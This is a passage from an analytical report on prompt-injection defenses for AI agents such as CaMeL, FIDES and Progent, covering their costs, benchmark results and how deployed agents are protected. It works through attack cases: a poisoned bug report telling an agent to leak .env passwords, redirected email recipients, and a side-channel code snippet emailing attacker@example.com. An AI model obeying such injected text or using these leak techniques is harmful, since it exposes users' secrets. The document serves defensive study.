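| CHERI | Not yet | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ | ✗ |
| Secure file transfer | Not by 2003 | – | ✓ | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ | ✓ |
| Policy Zones | Yes, at Meta | – | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ | ✗ | ✗ | ✓ |
| Safe types for queries and pages | Yes, at Google | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ |
| Rust in Android | Yes, in new code | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ |
| Browser sandboxes | Yes | ✗ | – | ✓ | ✗ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ |
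| HTTPS | Yes | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ |
| SSH | Yes | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ | ✓ |
| **Wrong predictions** | | **4** | **1** | **3** | **4** | **3** | **4** | **3** |

Some of these marks are debatable. The VAX kernel counts against the non-event explanation because it could have saved customers from buying several computers, a visible benefit. Policy Zones counts in favor of the threshold explanation because Ozment and Schechter's model allows for a single organisation large enough to pass the threshold on its own.

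Split costs has the best record, with one wrong prediction, but it is also the easiest explanation to fit after the event. Once we know that Google adopted something, we can easily find a way Google gained. The explanation works best combined with compatibility. A guarantee tends to spread when the people who have to do the work gain enough to justify it, and compatibility largely determines how much work there is. This is close to saying that people do what benefits them, but it specifies that the gain has to go to the people doing the work, so a large benefit to society or to end users may not be enough.

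The threshold still explains CHERI and other technologies that need several industries to act together, and the wrong threat still explains the Orange Book's higher classes well. Hidden quality and non-events probably reduce demand for all security, but they explain little about why people choose detection, except that alerts make a detector's work easier to see.

Fourteen cases cannot establish which of seven overlapping causes mattered most. The cases are hand-picked, and anyone filling in the table already knows how they ended. Google was behind several of the successes, so they are not independent. Whether a case counts as a success also depends on when it is judged. HTTPS would have been among the failures in 2006, when Ozment and Schechter counted fewer than 300,000 HTTPS certificates, compared with 40 million registered .com names, and concluded that credit card companies' requirements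 had not pushed HTTPS past its tipping point.

Comparisons between similar cases are better evidence, because more of the circumstances stay the same. SSH spread faster than secure file transfer, pledge spread further than Capsicum, and HTTPS grew quickly after certificates became free and automatic. In each pair, the version that required less of its adopters did better, even though pledge offered a weaker guarantee than Capsicum. But none of these was a controlled experiment. OpenBSD's leader campaigned for pledge, and browser makers were pressuring websites while certificates were becoming free.

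## How do structural defenses against prompt injection work, and what do they cost?

Parameterised queries use a database language's grammar to keep commands apart from data, but a language model has nothing comparable. The software around an agent joins the user's request and everything the agent reads into one text, and the model may follow an instruction in any part of it. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, writes that there is no known reliable way to make a model obey one category of text while safely processing another. Narisetty and colleagues cite measurements showing that neither prompting nor further training reliably creates this separation.

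Training has made models much harder to mislead. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) reports that only 0.2% of 935 existing attacks succeeded against an agent running OpenAI's GPT-5.2 with no added defense. But a low success rate for known attacks doesn't guarantee a low rate for new ones, so structural defenses are designed on the assumption that some attacks will mislead the model.

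### Six design patterns

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six designs based on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. The designs follow this principle to different degrees.

| Pattern | How it works | What injected text can still do |
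|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Nothing, if it arrives in a result |
| Plan, then execute | The model commits to a list of tool calls before it reads anything untrusted | Change what an email says, but not a recipient named in the plan |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Get its own document wrongly included |
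| Two models | One model plans, and another without tools reads the untrusted text | Change the values that the reading model extracts |
| Code, then execute | The planning model writes a program that handles the untrusted text | Change the values that the program passes on |
| Context minimisation | The system deletes the user's message before the model writes its answer | Influence the earlier step that used the message |

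A shop's chatbot that only sends customers links to their orders or settings can use the action-selector pattern. An assistant that searches files for invoices and emails them to the accounts department needs more freedom, so the map-reduce pattern suits it better. A malicious file can cause the assistant to count it as an invoice, but it cannot make the assistant email other files to the attacker.

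With these defenses, the agent can no longer perform arbitrary tasks. Willison's blog post *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) acknowledges that this trade-off is not popular, but considers it realistic while nobody has a better solution.

### From two models to a program

Willison proposed the two-model pattern in April 2023. A privileged model plans how to carry out the user's request and can use tools, but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model processes that text and has no tools. Ordinary software carries results between them. When the quarantined model summarises an email, the privileged model receives only a name such as `$summary1`. It can use that name to have the software display the summary to the user.

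Researchers at Google DeepMind found a gap in this design. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes. An attacker who can edit the notes adds text that makes the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead. The privileged model's plan stays the same, but the agent sends the document to the attacker.

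Their own system, CaMeL, addresses this by turning the request into a program in a restricted version of the language Python. For Bob's document, the privileged model might write:

```
notes = find_notes("last meeting")
address = ask_quarantined("Bob's email address", notes)
title = ask_quarantined("document Bob requested", notes)
send_email(to=address, attachment=fetch(title))
```

CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, which records that `address` came from `notes`. A policy can then allow `send_email` only if the recipient is someone the user already trusts. For any other address, the system asks the user. CaMeL calls the tags on each value capabilities, but they record where the value came from and who may read it, so they resemble the labels of information-flow control more than the keys in KeyKOS.

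Somebody has to write and maintain these policies. Willison, who has worked on web security for two decades, says he has trouble thinking through such rules himself. He also worries that users who receive many approval requests will start to approve everything.

### Checking labels before each call

Microsoft's FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) describe in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, attaches an integrity label (trusted or untrusted) and a confidentiality label to every piece of data. The agent's context, which is everything currently in its main model's input, takes the most restrictive combination of the labels on its contents. Before each tool call, ordinary code compares the labels with the tool's policy.

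FIDES can also hide data in variables, as the two-model pattern does, but it hides only data that would make the context's label more restrictive. The main model can query a quarantined model about a hidden value and restrict the answer to a fixed type. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. The main model queries the quarantined model for a yes or no on whether there is a request. If the answer is yes, the main model passes the meeting's details to the calendar without reading them.

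A yes-or-no answer carries one bit of information, and a choice among eight options carries three. Neither can hold a new instruction, so a policy can let the agent act on the answer even though untrusted text influenced it. An attacker can still cause a false yes or put false details in the calendar.

### A poisoned bug report

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) shows how FIDES handles one attack. In the example, an agent sorts the bug reports, or issues, filed on a public software project. It can read issues, read and write the project's files, and post public comments.

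An attacker files a plausible report about a failed build. At the end, a note imitates a system message and claims that the user has authorised access to the project's secrets. It tells the agent to read `.env`, a file that often contains passwords, and post the contents as a reply. Suppose the model follows the note:

| Step | Tool call | Label on the result | Context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
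| Start | None | None | Trusted, public |
| 1 | `read_issue` | Untrusted, public | Untrusted, public |
| 2 | `read_file(".env")` | Trusted, private | Untrusted, private |
| 3 | `post_comment` with the passwords | Blocked | Untrusted, private |

FIDES allows step 2 because reading the file does not send it anywhere. It blocks step 3 because `post_comment` accepts only public data and the context is now private. The user then sees an approval request that names the tool and the label responsible. Rewording the note would not change this result. If the note had told the agent to overwrite a file, FIDES would have blocked that call too, since `write_file` does not accept untrusted input.

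The policy on comments currently covers only private data. To stop an attacker from dictating a misleading public comment, the developer would also have to make `post_comment` refuse untrusted input. The agent would then need approval for any comment based on an issue it had read, and writing such comments is much of its job.

In the example, the main model can read the issue's text. By default, FIDES instead replaces that text with a variable, so the attacker's note never reaches the main model. This requires a second model call, and the main model has to work from summaries.

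Confidentiality labels can also list the people allowed to read something. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example with no attacker at all. Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. One is from Priya and previews the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but may not see them yet. Each email's readers are its sender and Alex, so the readers of any text based on both emails are

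{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}.

The agent may send a message on its own only if every recipient is in this set. Marco is not, so FIDES stops the reply. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the result would be {Alex, Priya, Marco} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex, Marco}, and the reply could go out. But the rule would also stop a reply to Marco about lunch if the agent had read Priya's email first. Earlier systems had the same problem, known as label creep.

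### Progent's rules for each call

CaMeL and FIDES change how the agent plans. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) can be added to an existing agent, because it places a check between the agent and its tools. Each Progent rule names a tool and the arguments that tool may receive. For example, a rule might let the agent send a Slack message only to Alice. Progent blocks any call that matches no rule.

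The right rules depend on the task, so a language model writes them from the user's request and revises them as the agent learns more. Injected text could mislead this model too. Progent therefore uses a solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, to compare the calls allowed by the old and proposed policies. An update takes effect automatically only if the new policy allows no call that the old policy blocks. Any other update needs approval from a person or a preset rule.

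Suppose a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. At first, the policy allows only a search for that email. The list requires reading recent mail and posting a summary on Slack, so the model proposes adding those tools to the policy, and the solver flags the change as an expansion. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. If the model proposes a rule allowing this, the solver flags that too. In tests on one benchmark, only 6% of policy updates were expansions.

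Progent guarantees that permissions do not grow without approval, but not that the permissions are right. An approver who accepts everything removes much of the protection. Similarly, *SPA* (2026) argues that detailed policies for each tool can express more than a simple comparison of labels, but their guarantee depends on each policy being correct and complete.

### Benchmark results

Researchers usually test these systems on AgentDojo, a set of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts, with attacks planted in the data. Shi and colleagues also used the ASB benchmark. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks.

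| Defense | Source | Setting | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Narisetty and colleagues, citing its developers | AgentDojo, OpenAI's o3 | None within its threat model | 77%, against 84% undefended |
| CaMeL with policy checks | Garby and colleagues | Banking tasks, two newer models | None | 37.5%, about half the rate without checks |
| FIDES with policy checks | Costa and colleagues | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 0, against 152 undefended | 50%, against 84% (averages of the four suites) |
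| Progent | Shi and colleagues | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 1.0%, against 39.9% | Similar to undefended |
| Progent | Shi and colleagues | ASB, GPT-4o | 3.9%, against 70.3% | Similar to undefended |
| Progent | Narisetty and colleagues | Part of AgentDojo, Qwen2.5-7B | 4.2%, against 25.8% | 27.1%, against 45.2% (under attack) |

CaMeL also used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens. Tokens are the units of text that AI companies usually charge for.

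How many tasks an agent can still complete under these defenses depends heavily on the kind of work. Costa and colleagues found that in 5% of the office tasks and 44% of the banking tasks, the agent has to see untrusted data before it can choose its next step. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policies are meant to prevent. The choice of model also matters. FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1 and 41% with GPT-4o, because o1 was better at working with variables.

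The policy checks provide FIDES's security guarantee. Without them, FIDES let 21 attacks through, about as many as the best heuristic defense in the comparison. The variables help the agent complete more tasks under that guarantee. FIDES completed 50% of tasks, compared with about 42% for an ordinary agent with the same checks.

Security scores can also overstate how much protection a design provides. Garby and colleagues point out that about two thirds of the banking attacks need a tool that the user's task never calls for, so a plan made in advance defeats them even without data tracking. One task, however, required the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. CaMeL's planning model wrote a program that looked up each instruction in the file and called the matching tool. With the policy checks off, an attacker could use those tools despite the separation between the two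 models.

*The Devil is in the Context* (2026) tested several defenses on newly generated cases. Attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time with no defense and 2.5% of the time with CaMeL, but CaMeL completed only 27.5% of the tasks. PromptArmor, which uses a language model to find and remove injected instructions, let 7.5% of attacks through and completed 90% of the tasks. The percentages suggest a test of about 40 cases, so CaMeL may have let through one attack and PromptArmor three. Many companies would reasonably choose PromptArmor based on these results, but they are weak evidence of how it would perform against attacks designed to get past it.

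Narisetty and colleagues ran such an adaptive attack on Progent in June 2026. Their injected text presented the harmful action as a routine step the user had already approved, to try to get Progent's rule-writing model to allow it. The attack succeeded 2.6% of the time, less often than the standard attack. The researchers suspect the disguise also made the agent less likely to act on the instruction.

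This evidence is encouraging but limited. The test used one attack template, a small model and eight tasks from each of three suites, and the agent ignored every attack in one suite even without a defense. The testers did not try an attack that uses only permitted tools. Progent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The testers work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on the same principle, although they openly acknowledge these weaknesses.

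### What the defenses leave open

A defense that controls an agent's actions does not make the agent's text accurate. If an email tells the quarantined model to write an empty summary, FIDES may deliver it to the right person. CaMeL's developers explicitly exclude such harms. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* planted false data instead of instructions, imitating the markers that separate one item from the next. These attacks succeeded 49.1% of the time against GPT-5.2 with no added defense. They succeeded 25.0% of the time against CaMeL without its policies, because the quarantined model extracted the wrong values.

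Restricting the format of an answer helps only if the format cannot contain instructions. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a coding agent could read outside documentation only as a list of functions with names of up to 30 characters. Willison wonders whether an attacker could still do damage with a function called `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance()`, which refers to `rm -rf`, the Unix command for deleting a folder and everything in it.

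**Side channels.** CaMeL's developers demonstrated two ways to leak information past their own system. Garby and colleagues describe another, which uses an implicit flow. In this example, `balance` is secret:

```
hint = True
rich = True
if balance > limit: hint = False
if hint: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker@example.com", "yes")
```

If the balance is above the limit, `hint` becomes false and its label becomes secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, no email goes out. The attacker learns whether the balance is above the limit, although no data labeled secret ever reached the email tool.

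Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and used the proof checker Lean to prove that it prevents such leaks. The proof does not cover what an attacker can learn from whether a program finishes.

Labels can be wrong because a user pastes in hostile text or because a developer forgets to label a tool. Microsoft's released version of FIDES treats an unlabeled tool as trusted and public. Microsoft is considering the opposite default, which would be safer but would block more work until developers had labeled everything. Deliberate labels can also be too generous. Microsoft and GitHub label everything in a private code repository as trusted, including any customer email that an employee has copied into an issue.

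Some tasks require the agent to follow instructions in untrusted content. If a user asks it to pay whatever an attached invoice says, the invoice's author controls the payment. The system can ask the user to approve the payment, but the user may be too busy to check or may believe the invoice. Narisetty and colleagues call this the deepest open problem in the field, because nobody has a principled account of which such tasks can be made secure.

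### Attempts to recover lost utility

One approach is to arrange the agents so that labels spread less. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated groups of agents, without using language models. The agents divided tool calls among themselves and passed the results to one another. Once an agent handled sensitive data, it stayed labeled as sensitive, and the researchers counted how many tool calls this affected.

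Fewer calls were affected when agents could communicate directly, because no intermediary picked up the label. Restricting the sensitive tools to a few agents also helped. But linking every pair of *n* agents directly requires *n*(*n* − 1)/2 connections, or 10 for five agents and 190 for twenty, and each needs monitoring. Even the best arrangement still affected some calls, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that agents also need declassification.

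*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) aims to keep restrictive labels out of the main context. When the agent needs to read something untrusted, it can start a temporary copy of itself. The copy takes on the untrusted label, returns an answer from a fixed set and shuts down, so the original agent's label doesn't change. If a check blocks a call, APPA looks for an approved way to proceed, such as removing personal details or asking an authorised person to permit that one call.

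The agent completed between 64.2% and 91% of its tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs. If those runs were independent, the true attack success rate could be as high as about 0.23% at 95% confidence, and an attacker who adapted to APPA might do better. A copy that has read hostile text can also return a false answer if that answer is on the list.

Garby and colleagues let the planning model mark particular untrusted values as acceptable, which they call endorsement. The model must do this in its plan, before it sees any untrusted text. Their agent completed about twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL with policy checks, and attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment using details in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, the agent blocked this attack but also failed at legitimate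 tasks of the same kind.

The system in *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) instead checks each call just before it runs, examining where the data came from and whether the user's request authorises the effect. Across eight benchmarks, its task completion rate fell by at most three percentage points. But the tested version can restore a call that the data-origin check has blocked, so it lacks the full guarantee proved for a stricter version.

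FlowSeal, a defense against privacy leaks, comes similarly close to normal performance, but its threat model excludes prompt injection. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) report that it completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defenses they tested, and leaked at most 3.3% of the private items. FlowSeal checks every attempt the agent makes to write or share data, regardless of the model's output. When the agent has used private records, a separate language model checks whether the proposed message reveals them, so part of the protection is still heuristic.

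## What do deployed AI agents rely on, and how well does it hold?

Few of these designs protect the agents that people use every day. McKerchar wrote in *Inside the lethal trifecta* in spring 2026 that none of the mainstream coding agents, including Claude Code, Cursor, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI, had adopted CaMeL or the two-model pattern. Companies instead combine training, detection, user approval and isolation, though users often have to turn on the isolation themselves.

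### From prototype to default

| Measure | What it does | Stage by late 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Model training | Teaches the model to ignore instructions in outside text | Default, since it is part of the model |
| Classifiers | Check what the agent reads and writes for signs of an attack | Default in some products |
| Approval prompts | Ask the user before a risky action | Default in most coding agents |
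| Sandboxes and network limits | Restrict the files and addresses the agent can reach | Default in some products, opt-in in others |
| Restricted modes | Switch off some tools or log-ins | Opt-in |
| Filtering by author | Hides text by people the project does not trust | Default for public projects in one GitHub service |
| Information-flow labels | Track data and block forbidden flows | Opt-in and experimental |
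| CaMeL | Runs the user's request as a program with data tracking | Prototype |

The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body whose members include Anthropic, Google, Meta, Microsoft and OpenAI, divides security measures for agents into probabilistic controls, such as classifiers, and deterministic ones, such as sandboxes and network rules (*Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents*, 2026). It advises that agent security "should not rely on detection alone", but adds that agents may not be useful enough with deterministic controls alone.

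Sandboxes are the most widespread deterministic control. According to McKerchar, most coding agents include one but leave it off by default. In Claude Code, for example, the operating system can enforce limits on file and network access, but the user has to turn them on with a command. OpenAI's Codex is an exception, because it runs commands in a sandbox without network access unless the user changes the settings. *Under the hood* (2026) describes how GitHub's Agentic Workflows, a service that runs agents automatically on software projects, puts the agent in a separate container with a firewall between it and the internet.

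A sandbox does little to stop an agent from misusing the access it needs for its job. If the agent holds a password and can reach the internet, it can send the password to an attacker. McKerchar recommends giving the agent a sealed tool instead of the password. The agent might call `firewall.list_rules()`, and a separate program that holds the password would build the request in a fixed format and return only the answer. The agent can choose the tool and its parameters, but not the address the request goes to. Cloudflare's bindings work similarly. McKerchar found no single project that supplied the whole arrangement.

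Restricted modes remove abilities in advance. Willison calls the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate with the outside world the "lethal trifecta". An attacker needs all three to steal data. Meta's "Agents Rule of Two", published in 2025, advises developers to let an agent have at most two of three similar properties without human supervision. The Forum notes that some developers offer a logged-out mode, in which an agent acts without the user's credentials. In February 2026 OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people at high risk. Among other restrictions, it limits web browsing to stored copies of pages. These modes protect people who know they need them, but most users never turn on a setting that limits what a product can do.

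Google has put part of a structural design into Chrome. In December 2025 it described new protections that limit the browser's agent to websites relevant to the user's task. The component that decides which sites are relevant does not see the text of web pages, so a hostile page cannot use its text to get itself approved. Another model, which also does not see the pages, checks whether each proposed action serves the user's goal. Google said that CaMeL and the two-model pattern partly inspired this second check. The check still depends on a model's judgment, so it does not offer CaMeL's guarantee.

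### A detector and labels in the same server

GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect agents to tools, offers both a detector and information-flow labels, which allows an unusually direct comparison of the two.

The detector looks for passwords and keys in the data that agents send to and from public code repositories. GitHub (2025) announced that the hosted server blocks a call by default if the detector finds one, although the user can usually override the block.

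To get labels from the same server, a developer has to add a special line to its configuration. The server then labels each result but does not enforce the labels. According to the documentation of GitHub's label code on pkg.go.dev, a separate service enforces them. GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line agent, can do this, but only if the user starts it with another experimental setting. Microsoft, which worked with GitHub on the feature, says it does not yet cover all of the server's tools or support other servers.

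The secret scanner became a default while the labels remained opt-in, because the scanner works as soon as GitHub turns it on, whereas labels do nothing until the server supplies them and the agent's software acts on them. But the scanner protects against less. It would miss an agent summarising a confidential plan in a public comment, because the summary contains nothing that looks like a password.

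GitHub has made some of the labels stricter than Microsoft first described. GitHub's published code marks issue text as untrusted even in private repositories, so a customer email pasted into an issue no longer counts as trusted. The code still marks material in those repositories as trusted if only collaborators can add it, as with files, commits and releases.

### FIDES since May

On 20 May 2026, Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Developers had to turn FIDES on.

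According to Microsoft's announcement, results from a tool that a developer forgets to label count as trusted and public. In the documentation, they count as untrusted but still public. This change makes a forgotten label much less dangerous when an attacker tries to control the agent, because the agent cannot use untrusted results to trigger a protected action. But the new default doesn't protect confidentiality. If the unlabeled tool returns payroll records, FIDES still treats them as public and may let the agent post them.

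According to its documentation, FIDES is available only for Python, with a version for Microsoft's .NET platform to follow. The documentation also describes a dry-run mode, which records what FIDES would have blocked without blocking it. Meta used a similar mode to introduce Policy Zones.

Microsoft has kept working on FIDES. Releasebot's *Agent Framework Updates & Release Notes* (2026), a copy of the company's notes, lists several fixes in October and November. For instance, FIDES now stops when a tool's policy is invalid and rejects conversation histories that it cannot match to its own records. A new option for labeling messages, added on 13 November, was still marked experimental. By comparison, Microsoft announced in July that Agent Skills, a feature that gives agents reusable instructions and scripts, was stable enough for production use in Python. Agent Skills may have been easier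 to finish.

### GitHub hides what strangers write

Unlike Copilot CLI, Agentic Workflows uses integrity labels by default. GitHub gives each issue, comment and code change a level based on its author and on whether the project's maintainers have accepted it. The levels, from highest to lowest, are merged, approved, unapproved, none and blocked. In a public repository, the service removes everything below "approved" before it reaches the model, unless the project chooses another threshold. By default, this keeps a stranger's comment from the agent whether or not it contains an attack.

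GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* explains why GitHub didn't rely on searching text for attacks. Attackers can rephrase their instructions or split them across several fields, and maintainers have to keep deciding how many harmless comments they are willing to lose. The filter instead uses a small reference monitor that compares labels without interpreting them. GitHub already records who owns and contributes to each project, so maintainers don't have to label anything by hand.

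The filter has large gaps. An agent that sorts bug reports from the public has to read what strangers write, so its owner must lower the threshold and give up much of the protection. Private repositories have no threshold by default. An attacker who takes over a maintainer's account gets the maintainer's level of trust.

At the time of GitHub Next's article, the service also recorded where confidential data went but did not stop it from leaving. Aident's *How to Secure GitHub Agentic Workflows Against Prompt Injection* recounts an attack, published in July 2026, in which the security company Noma used a public issue to steer an agent that could read private repositories and post public comments. The attack was a demonstration rather than a theft, but it combined all three parts of the lethal trifecta. A confidentiality rule like the one in FIDES could have blocked the last step, posting the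 public comment.

### Twelve defenses under adaptive attack

Most deployed agents still depend heavily on the model, or a classifier running alongside it, to recognize attacks. In October 2025, Milad Nasr and colleagues from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several universities published a severe test of twelve such defenses, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. Some relied on special prompts or training, and others on filters. Some were meant to stop users from misusing a model rather than to prevent prompt injection.

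The researchers adapted their attacks to each defense and succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. McKerchar reports a 100% bypass rate for human testers, meaning that they eventually found a way past every defense, not that every attempt worked.

The test shows that a low success rate against a fixed list of known attacks is weak evidence of how well an agent would resist a skilled attacker. The agent may block the listed attacks because its developers trained it against them, yet fail against a new one. The test does not measure how often attacks succeed in daily use, where attackers often have less time and fewer chances to practise than these researchers did.

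### What happens when an attacker keeps trying

An attacker can usually send more than one malicious email. The best-known figures on repeated attempts are for Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic released in November 2025 and has since replaced several times. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that, in a test by the security firm Gray Swan, a single strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time, but attackers succeeded in 33.6% of cases within ten attempts and in 63.0% within a hundred. Rates for some rival models were as high as 92%.

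If attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in *m* attempts would be 1 − (1 − 0.047)^*m*, or about 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. This is much worse than the reported result.

The attempts were evidently not independent. Some combinations of task and attack goal were probably much harder to break than others, so an attacker who had failed many times was likely to be facing a hard one. A simple model shows how large this effect can be. Suppose that 63% of the targets are weak, and each attempt against them has a 7.5% chance of success, while the other 37% never give way:

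| Attempts | Independent attempts | Weak and strong targets | Reported |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 38% | 34% | 33.6% |
| 100 | 99% | 63% | 63.0% |

The close fit shows that an average success rate can combine targets that are fairly safe with others that an attacker can expect to break. An attacker who can tell them apart will concentrate on the weak ones. The fit doesn't prove that 37% of the targets were unbreakable, since other explanations could also fit three numbers. Some of those targets might have been broken after a thousand attempts, or by a better attack.

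The average success rate can also mislead when one attack reaches many people. If a million agents read the same poisoned web page and the success rate is 0.2%, the expected number of victims is 2,000. But many of those agents run the same model and may react the same way, so the actual number could be far lower or far higher.

### How much the models have improved

How often attacks on Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, succeeded depended strongly on the agent's job. According to VentureBeat, no attack succeeded in 200 attempts when the model worked in a restricted coding environment. When it operated a computer through the screen, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and attackers succeeded within 200 attempts in 78.6% of cases. Added safeguards lowered the 200-attempt rate to 57.1%, which is still far too high for an agent that handles anything valuable.

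Newer models do much better. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) reproduces results from a later Gray Swan benchmark:

| Model | Attack succeeds within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% |
| Meta's Muse Spark | 16.5% |
| OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% |
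| OpenAI's GPT-5.5 | 20.8% |

On a single attempt, the rate was 0.2% for Opus 5 and 0.5% for Opus 4.8. These figures come from Anthropic's system card, its report on tests of a new model, and Anthropic's own models did best in the comparison. The later benchmark may also differ from the test of Opus 4.5, so the drop from 4.7% to 0.2% may not be an exact measure of progress. The improvement from Opus 4.8 to Opus 5 is clearer because Gray Swan tested both in the same way.

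Protection also varies between companies' models. GPT-5.6 Sol was ten times as likely as Opus 5 to give way within 15 attack attempts, and was hardly better than GPT-5.5. A business that chooses its model for price or writing quality may get much weaker protection without noticing.

The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that in a separate test of browser agents, no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 scenarios. If those scenarios were a random sample of the attacks an agent might meet, the true success rate could still be as high as about 2.3% at 95% confidence. They weren't, and next year's attackers will try things the test did not include. OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

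Claude Opus 5.5 followed in September 2026. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every prompt injection test. It also warns that Opus 5.5 is more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. When Anthropic tested it without its usual extra safeguards, Opus 5.5 refused malicious requests less often than any other model in the comparison. Resisting injected text is therefore different from refusing harmful requests in general.

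Some of the progress comes from detectors outside the model. Anthropic tested its browser agent against an automated attacker that adapted its attacks and had 100 attempts in each environment. With Opus 4.5 alone, 8.0% of attacks succeeded. The company's original safeguards reduced this only to 7.6%, but improved ones reduced it to 1.4%. The new safeguards helped weaker models even more, reducing Sonnet 4.5's rate from 13.8% to 1.9%. These percentages count individual attacks, so an attacker who used all 100 attempts in one environment had more than a 1.4% chance of succeeding at least once.

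A company can combine several such layers. Boris Cherny, who leads work on Claude Code at Anthropic, said that Opus 5 with injection probes and Claude Code's Auto Mode reduced the attack success rate to "~0", according to ClawSouls' *The most exciting line was buried in a system card*. The probes look for signs of an attack in the model's internal activity, and Auto Mode uses a classifier to decide which actions may go ahead without asking the user. The model, the probes and the classifier are all heuristic defenses. They protect best when they fail on different attacks, and much less if one message can mislead all three.

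### Asking the user

When neither training nor a sandbox settles whether an action is safe, most agents ask the user for approval. This only helps if the user reads the request. Microsoft writes that constant approval requests make people less vigilant, and McKerchar writes that people "rubber-stamp when asked too often". The Forum worries that prompts users click through may create an illusion of oversight.

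None of the three measured the effect, but Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code's users approved 93% of permission prompts. Most of what a coding agent asks to do is harmless, so a careful user would approve most of it too, and the figure doesn't prove carelessness. It does show how little practice users get at refusing. If an agent asks for approval 50 times a day and one request in a thousand is dangerous, the user will see a dangerous request about once in 20 working days, and it may look much like the harmless ones.

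Companies have responded in two ways. Anthropic's Auto Mode hands many of the decisions to a classifier, which replaces a tired person with a detector. Sandboxing makes some permission prompts unnecessary, because the agent cannot do serious damage inside the sandbox. Anthropic said in 2025 that sandboxing had reduced permission prompts by 84% in its own use of Claude Code, so in this case a guarantee made the product more convenient to use.

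Labels could have a similar effect, since the system needs to ask the user only when data is about to cross a boundary. Microsoft's researchers make this case for FIDES. But in the released version, the prompt does not show where the label came from, so a user who reads that the context is "untrusted" may not know which of twenty emails caused the problem. Microsoft lists this among the features it wants to improve.

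McKerchar suggests approving safe, frequent actions automatically and reserving human approval for rare and irreversible ones. For those, the user would confirm the exact request with a fingerprint or a passkey, so a compromised agent couldn't forge the approval. But the user could still misunderstand the request and approve it.

### Where the money goes

Established security companies have spent heavily on firms whose products filter the inputs and outputs of AI systems. In August and September 2025, SentinelOne agreed to buy Prompt Security, CrowdStrike agreed to buy Pangea, Check Point agreed to buy Lakera, and F5 agreed to pay $180 million for CalypsoAI. Palo Alto Networks completed its purchase of Protect AI in July. A few months later, Protect AI's injection detector was among the twelve defenses that Nasr and colleagues defeated.

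The purchases are evidence of what these companies expect to sell, not of what works. A filter, like other detectors, can be sold separately, whereas a design like CaMeL is part of the agent itself. The purchases also make detection's share of spending look larger than it is, because companies like Google and GitHub don't announce a price when they build isolation into their own products.

Microsoft also sells isolation. According to Collab365's *Microsoft adds security controls for AI agents inside Microsoft 365*, Windows 365 for Agents became generally available in June 2026 and runs each agent on an isolated computer in Microsoft's data centers. A detector announced at the same time, which looks for confidential data in the prompts agents receive, was only in preview. Isolated computers were probably ready sooner than labels because they are an old idea and leave the agent's own software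 unchanged.

### When detection may be enough

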